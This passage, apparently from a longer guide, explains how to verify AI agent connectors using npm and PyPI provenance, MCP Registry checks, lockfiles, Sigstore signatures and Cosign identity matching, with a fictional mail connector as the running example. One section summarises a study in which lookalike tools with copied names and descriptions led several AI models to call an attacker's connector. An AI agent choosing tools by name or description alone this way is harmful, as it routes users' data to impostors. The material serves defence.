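# Verifying AI agent connectors with Sigstore signatures, SLSA build attestations and npm and PyPI provenance

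## What an agent connector is and what has to be checked before it runs

An agent connector is a program that gives an AI agent access to a tool or a data source, such as a mailbox, a folder of files or a company database. Most connectors use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open protocol that AI applications use to discover and call the tools that connectors offer. The protocol's documentation calls such a program an "MCP server", which can mislead newcomers because many of these servers run on the user's own laptop. Anthropic's Claude Desktop application lists them under a menu item called "Connectors", according to the company's support pages.

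Developers publish many connectors as packages on npm, the main registry for JavaScript software, or on PyPI, its counterpart for Python. A package registry hosts files that almost anyone can upload and anyone can install. Stacklok makes software for running connectors, and its post *From unknown to verified*, written by a maintainer of the official MCP index, says that whoever starts a third-party connector is "executing someone else's code".

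The tools for checking a connector come from software development, where this problem long predates AI agents. Sigstore is a public signing service. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts, pronounced "salsa") is a framework for describing how well a producer protects the path from source code to finished package. npm and PyPI can store signed records of a package's origin alongside the package. An installer can often use these tools to establish which source repository and which build produced a connector, but not whether the connector behaves well.

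### A mail connector, from configuration to running process

Suppose that a small mail provider called Ternmail offers a connector that lets an AI agent search and send mail. The company, its package and its repository are fictional. Ternmail's setup page asks users to paste these lines into their AI application's configuration file:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": {
      "command": "npx",
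      "args": ["-y", "@ternmail/connector"]
    }
  }
}
```

The lines have the same form as the real example in Model Context Protocol's *Connect to local MCP servers*, which sets up a connector for files. "mail" is only a label. Each time the application starts, it runs the command `npx -y @ternmail/connector`.

npx is a launcher that comes with npm, and its first job is to work out which package the name refers to. The configuration gives no version number, so if there is no copy on the machine already, npx normally takes whatever Ternmail has most recently marked as the latest release. Before installing anything new, npx would ordinarily ask the user to confirm. npm added that question to catch mistyped package names, and `-y` switches it off. Deleting `-y` from the configuration would not bring the question back, because npx assumes a yes whenever its standard input is not a terminal,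 and here the AI application is using standard input for its own messages.

npx then downloads the package into a cache folder, along with its dependencies (the other packages its code relies on) and their dependencies in turn. A user who asks for one package may receive a hundred. Until recently, any of them could also run a script during installation. Attackers liked these install scripts because they did not have to wait for anyone to use the package, as GitHub, which runs npm, explained in a 2026 review of its defences. GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026) announced in July that npm version 12 no longer runs dependencies' install scripts unless the user allows them. This gives connector users only limited protection, because npx starts the package's main program moments after installing it, and attackers can put malicious code there instead.

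Finally, npx looks up which command the package provides and runs it. The connector is now a process on the user's machine, and the AI application exchanges messages with it through standard input and output, one message per line. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026), part of the current specification, defines this as the stdio transport. The process has the permissions of the user's own account. Claude Desktop asks for approval before the agent uses one of the connector's tools through the protocol, but the connector's own code can open a file or a network connection without that approval. Nobody inspects the code during this sequence, so any checks have to happen before the application runs the command.

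Python connectors work in much the same way. If Ternmail also published its connector on PyPI, the command might be `uvx ternmail-connector`. uvx is part of uv, Astral's package tool, and it installs the package and its dependencies in a temporary virtual environment and runs it. The environment keeps the connector's libraries separate from those of other projects but does not restrict what the process may do. According to Astral's *Tools*, uvx uses the latest version the first time, then reuses its cached copy until the user requests another version or the cache is cleared or refreshed. Two colleagues with identical configuration files can therefore be running different code. Adding an exact version to the name, as in `ternmail-connector@1.4.2`, removes that difference, and npx accepts the same notation.

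All of this concerns local connectors. A remote connector runs on its operator's computers, and the AI application reaches it over the network, usually through Streamable HTTP, the other standard transport that the Model Context Protocol (2025) specification defines. The user receives no file to check against a signature and has to trust the operator, who can change the code between requests.

The two kinds are now about equally common. The best count so far is a census of the official public index of connectors in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026), which found 24,135 connectors on 22 August 2026. Of these, 43.6 percent came only as a package to install locally, 49.7 percent were only remote, and 5.1 percent offered both. Connectors that run locally from npm, like Ternmail's, made up 30.7 percent, down from 35.1 percent in mid-July, although their number grew from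 5,804 to 7,414. Package checks therefore apply to a little under half of the listed connectors. That share may be shrinking, but two counts 39 days apart are weak evidence of a trend.

### How a release acquires its evidence

The checks an installer can make depend on how the developer published the package. Ternmail keeps its source code in a public GitHub repository, `ternmail/connector`. To release version 1.4.2, a maintainer tags a commit (one recorded state of the source) as `v1.4.2`. The tag triggers a build workflow, a script called `publish.yml` that GitHub's build service, GitHub Actions, runs on one of its own machines. The script fetches the source, installs the dependencies, runs the tests, builds the package and uploads it to npm.

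npm needs some way of knowing that the upload really comes from Ternmail. The older way is a stored password or access token, which thieves can steal and reuse. The newer way relies on an OIDC token (for OpenID Connect, a standard for proving identity online), a short-lived signed statement from the build service about which repository and workflow is running. PyPI's *Internals and Technical Details* gives an example in which the token carries the repository's name as one of its claims, and the registry checks the claims before it accepts anything.

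Trusted publishing uses these tokens. Ternmail enters its repository and the filename `publish.yml` in the package's settings, and npm then accepts uploads from that workflow without a stored secret. Since September 2026 a package can have several such entries, for instance one for stable releases and one for test versions, as GitHub's *Multiple trusted publishing configurations for npm* (2026) announced. npm still accepts ordinary tokens unless the maintainers switch them off, so a project's use of trusted publishing does not prove that a given release went through it.

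The signed evidence relies on two older ideas, digests and digital signatures. A digest is a short fingerprint computed from a file's contents, and changing even one byte of the file changes the digest. A digital signature is a value computed from data with a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the secret key signed exactly that data.

An attestation is a signed statement about a file. It identifies the file by its digest, so nobody can move the statement to another file without detection. If it records where the package was built, from which source and by which workflow, it is called provenance. Ternmail's workflow signs through Sigstore, which ties a temporary key to the workflow's identity and records the signing in a public log.

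A second, simpler kind of record is the publish attestation, which differs between the registries. The npm registry issues one when an authorised user publishes a package, according to npm's *Generating provenance statements*. On PyPI, it records that a particular trusted publisher uploaded the file, and PyPI's *Introduction* lists SLSA provenance as a separate type that a project may add.

Most packages have none of this. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* (2026), a study of four large registries including npm and PyPI, found that only 2.0 to 6.6 percent of packages, depending on the registry, had attestations on their latest release. npm produces provenance automatically for trusted publishing, but only if both the package and its repository are public. Ternmail's fictional release is therefore much better documented than most.

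### Four links between the configuration and the code's behaviour

A user who pastes Ternmail's configuration relies on a chain of four links, and evidence for one link does not support the others.

| Link | What has to match | What helps |
|---|---|---|
| Configuration to package | The name in the configuration and the package that Ternmail really publishes | Ternmail's own website, MCP Registry namespaces, an exact version |
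| Package to build | The digest of the downloaded file and the digest in a signed attestation | Sigstore signatures, `npm audit signatures`, PyPI attestations |
| Build to source commit | The repository, workflow and commit in the provenance and the ones the installer expects | SLSA provenance, SLSA Build levels |
| Source to trustworthy behaviour | What the code does and what the user wants done | No signature or attestation; only review of the code and limits on the process |

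The link from configuration to package has to be checked first, because the later checks are worthless if the configuration names the wrong package. Stacklok's post gives the made-up name `@modelcontextportocol/github-mcp-server`, with two letters swapped, as an example of a misspelling a hurried reader would miss. An attacker who registered such a name could build the package in a public repository with a proper workflow and obtain a valid attestation, which would correctly identify the attacker's repository.

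The MCP Registry, the official index, offers some protection by checking that whoever publishes an entry controls the GitHub account or internet domain in the entry's name. An entry beginning `io.github.ternmail/` can therefore come only from someone who controls Ternmail's GitHub account. The registry holds no code, only entries that point to packages or remote addresses. According to Model Context Protocol's *The MCP Registry*, it leaves code scanning to the package registries and to the marketplaces that reuse its entries.

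Between the build and the package, someone can replace the file or upload one that the official workflow never made. SLSA cites the attack on Codecov, a maker of code-testing tools. The attacker used leaked credentials to upload a malicious file to a location from which customers downloaded it directly. Provenance for that file would have shown that it did not come from the expected build.

On npm, the command `npm audit signatures` reports registry signatures and attestations separately. In the sample output in npm's documentation, all 1,267 packages of a project have valid registry signatures, while 74 have valid attestations. The registry's signature covers the step from npm to the user and contains nothing about the build, so the other 1,193 packages have no link to a build.

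The link from build to source commit matters because people review source code, not finished packages. For a package with provenance, npm's website shows the commit, the workflow file and the run that produced the package, along with an entry in a public log, according to npm's *Viewing package provenance*. Whoever installs the package still has to trust that the build service recorded these accurately. In the SolarWinds attack, another of SLSA's examples, intruders compromised the build platform and inserted malicious code during each build without changing the source. SLSA's Build levels grade how well a platform resists this sort of tampering. The idea is that people examine a few build platforms thoroughly, and software then checks that each of many thousands of packages came from one of them.

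None of these tools can show that the source code itself behaves in a trustworthy way. SLSA's catalogue includes a contractor at the cryptocurrency exchange SushiSwap who had legitimate access to the repository and committed a change that redirected funds to the contractor. A faithful build of that commit would have had an accurate build record, even though the code stole money. A second reviewer might have caught the change, and the newest version of SLSA adds a Source track for controls of this kind. These controls cover how a project accepts changes, but they cannot certify what the changes do. SLSA also explicitly excludes producers who make malicious software on purpose.

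Each dependency also has its own chain. A package's SLSA level is independent of those of its dependencies, so Ternmail's provenance can be flawless while a small library three steps down the dependency tree has no attestation.

### Integrity, origin and safety

People often call a package "verified" without adding in what respect. Three properties are worth keeping apart. Integrity means that the file is unchanged since someone computed its digest. Origin means who built the file, and from what source. Safety concerns what the program does once it runs. (SLSA uses "integrity" more broadly, for protection against tampering anywhere between the developer's intention and the finished package, which takes in much of what is called origin here.)

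Three incidents at Ternmail show how one property can fail while the others hold. In one, an attacker who controls a mirror (a server that redistributes npm's packages) alters the connector there. Integrity has failed because the file no longer matches the digest that Ternmail's workflow signed, and an automatic comparison detects the mismatch immediately.

In another case, a thief steals a maintainer's npm token and uploads a version 1.4.3 from a private computer. The user receives exactly the file that npm holds, so integrity is intact, but the file's origin is wrong. The missing provenance is a sign of this, because npm accepts provenance only from builds on supported cloud services. A more careful thief would get valid provenance by running a workflow in another repository. To catch that release, an installer has to compare the repository's name with `ternmail/connector`, because checking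 only that an attestation exists would let it through.

A connector can also pass both the integrity and origin checks and still steal mail. Suppose a Ternmail employee adds a line that sends a copy of every message to an outside address, commits it to the official repository and publishes the connector through `publish.yml`. The digest would match, and the provenance would show the right repository, workflow and commit.

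The Open Source Security Foundation's *Build Provenance for All Package Registries* (2023) recommends that registries show that a package has provenance without implying that it is automatically trustworthy. PyPI's *Security model and considerations* says that a valid signature proves the signer had access to the named identity while the package was being built. An intruder who gains control of Ternmail's workflow also has that access.

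Even so, the evidence lets the user judge a named repository, whose code and history anyone can read, instead of a file from an unknown machine. The user can also notice if the next release comes from somewhere else. In the employee's case, the theft would at least be visible in a public commit.

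## Finding out which package a connector's name leads to

A user who wants to run Ternmail's connector needs its exact package, version and digest before looking at any signature. Writing these down helps, because every later check uses them.

### From the configuration to a digest

One-click install links also include a label, which, like "mail" in Ternmail's configuration, does not affect what runs. SafeDep's *The State of MCP Registries* reproduces an install link for the code editor Cursor that has one parameter for the connector's name, "Vercel", and another for its configuration. The configuration is encoded, so users cannot read it at a glance. Anyone who writes such a link can pair a familiar name with any command, so users have to check the configuration that the link produces to see what will run.

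The package name is in `args`. When the command is `npx` or `uvx`, it is normally the first item that is not an option, here `@ternmail/connector`. But npx's `--package` option and uvx's `--from` option allow the package and the command to have different names. For example, `uvx --from ternmail-tools ternmail-connector` installs the package `ternmail-tools`, which is the one to check. The `env` block is also worth checking, since a setting there can send npx or uvx to a different package registry. If the configuration has a `url` instead of a `command`, the connector is remote and there is no package.

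Ternmail's configuration gives no version, so the user has to choose one. The command `npm view @ternmail/connector version` prints the version that npm currently marks as the latest. Suppose that it is 1.4.2. This command then prints the digest:

```
npm view @ternmail/connector@1.4.2 dist.integrity
```

The result is a string that begins with `sha512-`. PyPI shows a SHA-256 digest for each file on a project's page. A Python release often has several files, such as one per operating system, and the digest to record is the one for the file the user's machine would install.

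For Ternmail, the finished record might look like this:

| Item | Value |
|---|---|
| Package | `@ternmail/connector` on npm |
| Version | 1.4.2 |
| Digest | The `sha512-` string that npm printed |
| Name in the MCP Registry | `io.github.ternmail/connector` |
| Repository that the provenance should name | `ternmail/connector` |
| Where these names came from | Ternmail's own website, with the date |

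The other rows depend on the last one, which is easy to leave out. A user who copied the package name from a forum post has established only which package the post named.

### How the MCP Registry ties an entry to a package

The MCP Registry offers a second route to the package name. Its entry for Ternmail's connector is a small file called `server.json`, shown here without the schema address that a complete file also has:

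```json
{
  "name": "io.github.ternmail/connector",
  "description": "Search and send Ternmail messages",
  "version": "1.4.2",
  "packages": [
    {
      "registryType": "npm",
      "identifier": "@ternmail/connector",
      "version": "1.4.2",
      "transport": { "type": "stdio" }
    }
  ]
}
```

Ternmail has to log in to publish under that name, and the login method determines which names it may use. According to Model Context Protocol's authentication guide, a GitHub login always allows names that begin with `io.github.` and the user's own account name. Only people with the Owner role in an organisation can use that organisation's names. Previously, any member could publish or overwrite entries under them.

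The alternative is to log in with an internet domain. The publisher creates a pair of keys, puts the public one in the domain's DNS records or in a file on the website, and signs the login with the private one. Ternmail could then call its entry `com.ternmail/connector`. Customers who know the company's website but not its GitHub account would find that name easier to judge.

The registry also checks the package itself. Model Context Protocol's *MCP Registry Supported Package Types* requires an npm package to carry a field called `mcpName` in its `package.json`, and the value must match the name in `server.json`:

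```json
{
  "name": "@ternmail/connector",
  "version": "1.4.2",
  "mcpName": "io.github.ternmail/connector",
  "repository": "github:ternmail/connector"
}
```

A Python package has no such field, so the registry looks for the text `mcp-name: io.github.ternmail/connector` in the README file, which PyPI displays as the project's description. The text may be in a comment that visitors to the page do not see.

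The entry now points to the package and the package points back to the entry, which is good evidence that the same publisher controls both names. An outsider cannot list Ternmail's package under another name, because the package does not contain that name, and cannot list a different package under Ternmail's name without access to Ternmail's account. But the user has to start from the entry, because anyone can copy the `mcpName` line into a package called `@ternmai1/connector`, with the digit 1 in place of the last letter of "ternmail". The line will look right even though no entry leads to that package.

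The check only compares names. It does not examine the code, show that anyone has reviewed the connector, or connect the package to its repository. The publisher writes the `repository` line in `package.json`, and Ternmail could build the package on a laptop from entirely different source code and still pass. Only provenance can confirm that line. The entry for an npm or PyPI package need not contain a digest (bundles, a separate package type, must have one), so the digest in the user's record has to come from the package registry.

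These ownership checks have also had bugs. GitLab's *Advisories for Golang/Github.com/Modelcontextprotocol/Registry package* describes one in which login tokens from GitHub's build service were valid on more than one installation of the registry software. Someone running a malicious installation could reuse a victim's token on another installation and publish under the victim's `io.github` name. GCVE's *OCI ownership validation fails open on upstream rate limits* describes another bug, which the maintainers rated low in severity. The registry skipped the ownership check for a container image if the service hosting the image refused a request because of too much traffic.

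The registry has been in preview since its launch in September 2025 (Model Context Protocol, 2025). At the end of November 2026 the official pages still carried warnings of breaking changes and possible data resets, so a user who relies on an entry should keep a copy. Model Context Protocol describes the registry as "quite permissive" in its moderation policy and says the maintainers remove only malware, spam, illegal content and completely broken servers.

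The rules on versions are stricter. A publisher cannot change an entry's version or other metadata after publication, and the registry refuses version strings that look like ranges, according to Model Context Protocol's versioning page. The example above has two `version` lines, one for the entry and one for the package. The registry recommends, but does not require, that they match, so the package's version is the one to record. The label "latest" can also mislead, because the registry always gives it to a new version whose string does not follow the usual numbering scheme, even if a higher number exists.

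The registry offers much less assurance for remote connectors. It does not verify that the publisher controls the address in the entry, and several publishers may list the same address. The Model Context Protocol project warns against inferring ownership or endorsement from a shared address.

### Lookalike names and lookalike tools

Ownership checks do not stop an attacker from using an account they own to register a name similar to a legitimate connector's. The owner of a GitHub account called `ternmail-app` can publish `io.github.ternmail-app/connector`, point it to their own package, and pass every check described so far.

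Many users never see the official entry, because the Model Context Protocol registry is designed mainly for marketplaces that copy its data. UpGuard, a company that sells risk-monitoring software, sampled 847 connectors on one such marketplace, Smithery, and found that 8 percent carried the badge for official vendors. Most independent developers would have no badge either, so a missing badge is little evidence of an impostor. UpGuard also points out that if a marketplace's names are case-sensitive, an attacker can register `hubspot` next to the real `HubSpot`. The trick doesn't work on the underlying package names, because npm doesn't allow capitals in new ones and PyPI ignores case. This is another reason to record the package rather than the title on a marketplace page.

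Similar confusion can arise after installation, because an AI agent often has several connectors running at once. The model picks a tool by its name, description and schema (the inputs it accepts). Li and Gao (2025), in *Toward Understanding Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol Ecosystem*, found that the applications they analysed carry out the model's choice without verifying it. If two connectors offer tools with the same name, the application may call the wrong one.

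In *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026) measured how often this failure, which they call "tool-provider misbinding", happens. They set up a legitimate connector, with a tool for fetching and storing a dataset, and an attacker's connector. The attacker's tool had either the same name as the legitimate one or an unrelated name. Its description was unrelated, copied, or copied with added claims such as "officially verified", and its schema either fitted the task or did not, which makes twelve combinations. For each combination, they gave five models ten differently worded requests and repeated each request five times, for 50 trials per model.

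When the attacker's tool shared only a name with the trusted one and had an unrelated description and an unsuitable schema, no model chose it in more than 2 percent of trials. When both the name and description were copied and the schema fitted, GPT-5.4, Qwen3.7 Max and DeepSeek V3 chose it every time. Gemini 2.5 Pro chose it in 84 percent of trials, and Claude Sonnet 5 chose it in 6 percent and asked the user for clarification in the rest. Half of the requests stressed the trusted destination or the intended provider, but this evidently made no difference for the three models that always chose the attacker's tool.

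The attack can work even when the tools don't share a name. DeepSeek V3 selected an attacker's tool with an unrelated name, a fitting schema and a description full of official-sounding claims in 50 percent of trials. Gemini 2.5 Pro selected it in 42 percent, GPT-5.4 in 4 percent and Claude Sonnet 5 in none. These rates come from a single task with the attacker's connector already in place, so they do not predict how often users will meet the problem. But they show that checking Ternmail's package cannot guarantee that a request to send mail reaches Ternmail's code. Every other connector in the same application needs the same check, and it is better to remove the ones nobody uses.

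### How often a name comes to lead somewhere else

The package or address that a connector's name leads to may change over time. To measure how common this is, Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, downloaded the whole official registry in August 2026. It held 21,643 servers and 72,606 version records. (The other census from that month found 24,135 servers on 22 August. The counts may differ because they were taken on different days, but Kraishan does not give the day of the download.) In Kraishan's download, 8,900 servers had more than one version. Kraishan compared each version of these servers with the next, checking for changes in the description, packages and remote addresses.

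Just over half, 51.1 percent, had changed at least one of the three, and 40.6 percent had changed "silently", meaning that the identifiers stayed the same while the meaning or the destination changed. Kraishan counts every rewritten description as a silent change, and about nine in ten of the silently changed servers had rewritten descriptions. Many of these edits may only have improved the wording.

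In 9.4 percent of the servers with multiple versions, a later version removed a package that an earlier one had listed, and in 11.1 percent a later version added one. The registry name alone is therefore not a reliable record of what a user checked.

Kraishan also found that 370 of the 8,900 servers, or 4.2 percent, kept their name but moved their remote address to a different host. The share among remote connectors must be higher, because the 8,900 include servers with no remote address. Kraishan does not claim that any of these moves was malicious and thinks most were routine migrations, but the registry has no way to distinguish a migration from a takeover. A move affects only applications that look up the name again, because those that stored the old address would keep using it.

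Among the servers that changed at all, the median time to the first change was less than a day. The most important changes may not appear in these figures, because the registry does not record which tools a connector offers or what those tools do.

Kraishan also fetched source code for 14,353 of the servers and searched it for 31 patterns that suggest a weakness. Such searches produce many false alarms, so Kraishan checked 294 of the findings by hand and found that only 56 percent were real. The share ranged from 17 percent for command injection (input that ends up running as a command) to 93 percent for dependencies without a fixed version. One person did all the labelling, so the exact values are somewhat uncertain. After correction for false alarms, about 7.6 percent of the servers had a serious weakness, most often a network service open to anyone without a login. This is only loosely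 in line with the findings of Li and Gao, who identified 833 vulnerable servers among 67,057 entries in six registries. Kraishan cautions that differences between such counts may come from the detectors as much as from the software.

Servers with silent changes had almost three times the odds of a serious finding. Kraishan attributes both to loosely run projects, which seems plausible, though the data cannot confirm it. A project's popularity, measured by GitHub stars, did not correlate with its number of findings.

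### Pinning the connector and its dependencies

Checking version 1.4.2 doesn't help if the application later runs 1.4.3. An unpinned command can install the newer version on a new laptop or after the cache is cleared, and a configuration that ends in `@latest` explicitly requests the newest version. Published instructions often use such commands. For example, SafeDep's article shows a connector for fetching web pages that starts with `uvx mcp-server-fetch`, which specifies no version.

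The simplest fix is to change the last argument to `@ternmail/connector@1.4.2`. npm does not let a publisher reuse a version number, so that name and version keep referring to the same package.

This pins only one of perhaps a hundred packages. Ternmail's `package.json` might list a mail-parsing library at version `^2.1.0`, which allows 2.1.0 or anything newer below 3.0.0. If someone takes over that library and releases a malicious 2.1.1, the next fresh installation of Ternmail's unchanged connector will include it. Kraishan found unpinned dependencies in about 2.8 percent of servers, but counted only those with no version constraint at all. Ranges like `^2.1.0` are npm's default and far more common.

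A lock file solves this. It lists the exact version and digest of every package in the dependency tree. Ternmail's developers probably have one, but npm leaves the ordinary lock file out of published packages, so users have to create their own. In an empty folder, they run:

```
npm init -y
npm install --save-exact --ignore-scripts @ternmail/connector@1.4.2
```

This downloads the connector and its dependencies without starting any of them, and writes `package-lock.json`. The user can now compare the connector's digest in that file with the one in the record and carry out the signature checks. On another machine, `npm ci --ignore-scripts` installs exactly what the lock file lists and stops with an error if a digest does not match. The configuration then starts the installed file directly:

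```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": {
      "command": "node",
      "args": ["/home/ana/ternmail/node_modules/@ternmail/connector/dist/index.js"]
    }
  }
}
```

The last part of the path comes from the `bin` field in the connector's `package.json`. Because npx is no longer used, starting the application does not install anything.

For the Python version, `uv init` and `uv add ternmail-connector==1.4.2` create a similar file, `uv.lock`. The application can then use the command `uv` with the arguments `run --locked --project /home/ana/ternmail ternmail-connector`. With these arguments, `uv` exits with an error if the lock file no longer matches the project.

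A lock file preserves whatever the package registry served when the user created it, so a dependency that was already malicious stays in place. It does not affect code that the connector downloads while running, and it cannot pin remote connectors. For remote connectors, Kraishan suggests that applications remember the host they first connected to and alert the user if it changes, which helps only if that first host was the right one.

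Pinning also holds back security fixes, so somebody has to decide when to update. A cooldown, which refuses very recent releases, can help with the timing. When Ternmail releases version 1.5.0, the user can install it in a separate folder and compare the two lock files to see which dependencies changed along with the connector. The evidence for those packages needs checking again.

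## How a Sigstore signature is made and checked

The digest in a user's lock file comes from npm and identifies the file that npm served, but it doesn't show who built that file. Ternmail's attestation includes that information, but the user can rely on it only after checking its signature.

Older signing systems depended on a key that the developer kept for years. Users had to find the right public key, and a thief who copied the private one could sign malware with it until somebody noticed. Sigstore instead uses a key that exists for minutes and a certificate that records which workflow held it. Its two main services are Fulcio, a certificate authority (a service that vouches for who holds a key), and Rekor, a public log of signatures.

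### Signing version 1.4.2

When Ternmail's maintainer pushes the tag `v1.4.2`, the signing happens inside the build workflow without further human involvement. GitHub's *Introducing Artifact Attestations* (2024) and Sigstore's *Spec* for client software describe much the same sequence:

1. The signing client asks GitHub for an OIDC token, which names the repository and workflow that are running. This token is meant for Sigstore and is separate from the one that npm accepts for the upload.
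2. The client creates a temporary key pair in memory.
3. It sends Fulcio the public key, the token and proof that it holds the private key. Fulcio checks that GitHub really signed the token, then issues a certificate that ties the public key to the workflow's identity.
4. Fulcio submits the certificate to a certificate transparency log, a public list of the certificates it issues. The log returns a signed certificate timestamp, which is a promise to include the certificate, and Fulcio embeds the promise in the certificate.
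5. The client computes the package's digest, writes a statement that joins the digest to the provenance, and signs the statement with the private key.
6. It sends the signature and the certificate to Rekor, which checks the signature and adds an entry to its log.
7. The client deletes the private key.

The certificate is valid for ten minutes, according to *Details on npm provenance*, a technical note on how npm uses Sigstore. Ternmail therefore has no signing key to protect between releases. An attacker would have to steal the key from the build machine's memory and use it almost immediately or, more realistically, obtain a token.

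The client then packs the certificate, the signed statement and the evidence from the log into one JSON file called the Sigstore bundle. The bundle contains nothing secret. npm stores it alongside the package, and anyone can download it.

### The fields of the certificate

The certificate for Ternmail's release might contain these values. Most of the fields are extensions that Sigstore defined, and their full numbers begin with `1.3.6.1.4.1.57264`.

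| Field | Extension | Value |
|---|---|---|
| Issued by | | `O=sigstore.dev, CN=sigstore-intermediate` |
| Valid | | 12 November 2026, 09:14:05 to 09:24:05 GMT |
| Subject Alternative Name | | `https://github.com/ternmail/connector/.github/workflows/publish.yml@refs/tags/v1.4.2` |
| Issuer (the identity provider) | `.1.8` | `https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com` |
| Build Signer URI | `.1.9` | The same address as the Subject Alternative Name |
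| Runner Environment | `.1.11` | `github-hosted` |
| Source Repository URI | `.1.12` | `https://github.com/ternmail/connector` |
| Source Repository Digest | `.1.13` | The identifier of the commit |
| Run Invocation URI | `.1.21` | The web address of this particular run |
| Source Repository Visibility At Signing | `.1.22` | `public` |

The Subject Alternative Name is the signing identity. It combines the repository, the workflow file and the git ref, which here is the tag. The word "issuer" has two meanings. Fulcio issued the certificate, but the Issuer field names the service that confirmed the workflow's identity, here GitHub Actions.

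The certificate's fields are harder to falsify than the provenance statement because Fulcio takes them from GitHub's token. The build process itself writes the statement, so someone who tampers with the environment variables during the build can make it wrong. *Details on npm provenance* explains that npm compares the two and rejects the package if they disagree.

The signing identity and the source repository can also differ. GitHub lets one project call a workflow that another project maintains, and the signing identity then refers to that workflow. Thousands of unrelated projects may share such an identity, so a user has to check the Source Repository URI as well.

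### Checking the bundle

Once the user has the package file and its bundle, an official client such as Cosign, Sigstore's command-line tool, checks the signature. Sigstore advises against writing a new verifier, because a correct one has many steps and each prevents a different kind of forgery.

The client first needs the trusted root, a file with the public keys of the real Fulcio and its logs and the dates between which each key is valid. It can't rely on keys from the bundle, because anyone can set up a private copy of Fulcio and issue certificates in Ternmail's name. The client downloads the trusted root through The Update Framework (TUF), a system for distributing signed updates, and verifies it using keys that came with the client. TUF also prevents an attacker from passing off an old version of the file as current.

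The client uses those keys to check the certificate chain, which confirms that Fulcio signed the certificate, directly or through an intermediate certificate. A certificate that a forger made without Fulcio's key fails this check. The client also checks the signed timestamp from the certificate log, which catches a certificate that someone made with a stolen Fulcio key but kept out of the log to hide it from Ternmail.

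A forger could instead copy Ternmail's genuine certificate, which is public, into a bundle with a different statement. The signature check would then fail, because a signature on the new statement that matches the certificate's public key could only be made with the private key, which has been deleted.

The client next checks that the certificate was valid at the time of signing, since it has usually been expired for weeks when a user installs the connector. The client takes the signing time from Rekor or a separate timestamping service, because a forger could write any time into the statement. Someone who recovers the temporary key a day later can still sign with it, but cannot get an honest service to date those signatures within the certificate's ten-minute validity period.

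The client also checks that Rekor has an entry with the same signature, certificate and digest as the bundle. Without this check, an attacker who controlled Ternmail's signing identity could sign a malicious package for one victim and keep the signature out of public view. The certificate log would show only that someone had obtained a certificate in Ternmail's name, not which file they signed with it.

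The client has not yet checked the package itself, so it computes the digest of the downloaded file and compares it with the digest in the statement. This stops an attacker from attaching Ternmail's genuine attestation to another file. npm's client also compares the package's name and version. Otherwise a mirror could serve version 1.3.0, which has a known security hole and a genuine attestation, as if it were 1.4.2.

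Finally, the client checks that the signing identity and issuer match the ones the user expects. Fulcio accepts identity tokens from several providers, so the issuer check confirms that the workflow's token came from GitHub.

Real clients order these steps differently. The Sigstore specification has the client establish the time first, because it must check the certificate chain as of that time. The order doesn't matter to the user, since any failure ends the verification.

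### A valid signature from the wrong repository

The user has to supply information only for the last comparison, but skipping it makes the others almost worthless. Suppose an attacker opens a GitHub account called `ternmail-tools`, copies Ternmail's source code into a repository named `connector`, and adds a line that forwards every message to an outside server. The attacker's workflow requests a token from GitHub, and the token correctly names `ternmail-tools/connector`. Fulcio then issues a certificate for it, and Rekor logs the signature.

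The resulting bundle passes every check except the last. The certificate is real, the signature is correct, the log contains the entry and the digest matches the malicious file. The attacker did not have to pay for anything or break into Ternmail. A program that reports "signed" after these checks has verified only that somebody with a GitHub account built the package. Sigstore describes this as a common failure.

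With Cosign, the user states the expected issuer and identity on the command line:

```
cosign verify-blob-attestation \
  --certificate-identity="https://github.com/ternmail/connector/.github/workflows/publish.yml@refs/tags/v1.4.2" \
  --certificate-oidc-issuer="https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com" \
  --new-bundle-format --bundle connector.sigstore.json \
  connector-1.4.2.tgz
```

The attacker's bundle fails this command because its certificate names another repository.

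The identity above contains the tag, so it fits one release only. For a rule that also covers later releases, Cosign accepts a pattern, such as the one that Sigstore's *cosign Verification of npm Provenance, GitHub Artifact Attestations, and Homebrew Provenance* uses for a real npm package. Patterns need care. `^https://github.com/ternmail`, with no slash at the end, also matches `ternmail-tools`. A pattern that lacks the opening `^` can match text anywhere in the identity, and the identity ends with a branch or tag name that the attacker chooses. Someone could run a workflow from a branch called `ternmail/connector/main` in an unrelated repository and satisfy the pattern `ternmail/connector/`. A safer pattern is:

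```
^https://github\.com/ternmail/connector/\.github/workflows/publish\.yml@refs/tags/v
```

The expected identity has to come from outside the bundle, for the same reason as the root keys. Sigstore's *The Importance of Verification* recommends that projects publish it in a place that only trusted people can change. The Python Software Foundation, for example, publishes a table of signed Python releases with each release manager's email address and the issuer. Few connector developers are likely to publish such a table. Ternmail's user can rely on the repository name recorded in the previous stage, if that name came from Ternmail's own website.

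### How an inclusion proof works

Rekor's log is far too large for each user to download, so Rekor supplies a short inclusion proof to show that the log contains a given entry. The proof is based on a Merkle tree, which combines the digests of neighbouring entries in pairs, then combines the resulting digests in the same way until a single digest, the root, remains.

In this example, a log has four entries, and Ternmail's is the third. Real logs use SHA-256, but to keep the arithmetic simple, digests here are two-digit numbers, and combining two of them means calculating 3 × left + 7 × right and keeping the last two digits.

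```
                 26
              /      \
          51            39
         /  \          /  \
       12    45      31    78
                      |
                  Ternmail
```

The client can calculate 31 from Ternmail's entry. The proof consists of two more numbers, 78 and 51, with their positions. The client combines 31 and 78: 3 × 31 + 7 × 78 = 639, which gives 39. It then combines 51 and 39: 3 × 51 + 7 × 39 = 426, which gives 26. The log has published 26 as its root in a signed statement called a checkpoint, so the proof succeeds. If somebody had altered the entry and its digest were 32, the same calculation would give 47.

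It would be easy to invent other numbers that also lead to 26 under this toy rule, but nobody knows how to do this with SHA-256. The proof also stays short as the log grows, because doubling the number of entries adds only one digest. For a log with a billion entries, the proof needs about 30 digests, which take up less than a kilobyte.

The tree also allows a consistency proof, which shows that existing log entries have not changed. Suppose a fifth entry arrives with the digest 60. The old root, 26, becomes the left half of the new tree, and the new root is 98, from 3 × 26 + 7 × 60 = 498. Anyone who kept the old root can repeat this calculation to confirm that the first four entries are unchanged.

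A dishonest log operator could still keep two trees, one for the victim and one for everyone else, and give valid proofs from each. The usual defence is independent witnesses, who sign a root only after checking that it extends the last one they saw. A client that requires their signatures will reject a tree the witnesses have never seen.

### The change to Rekor v2

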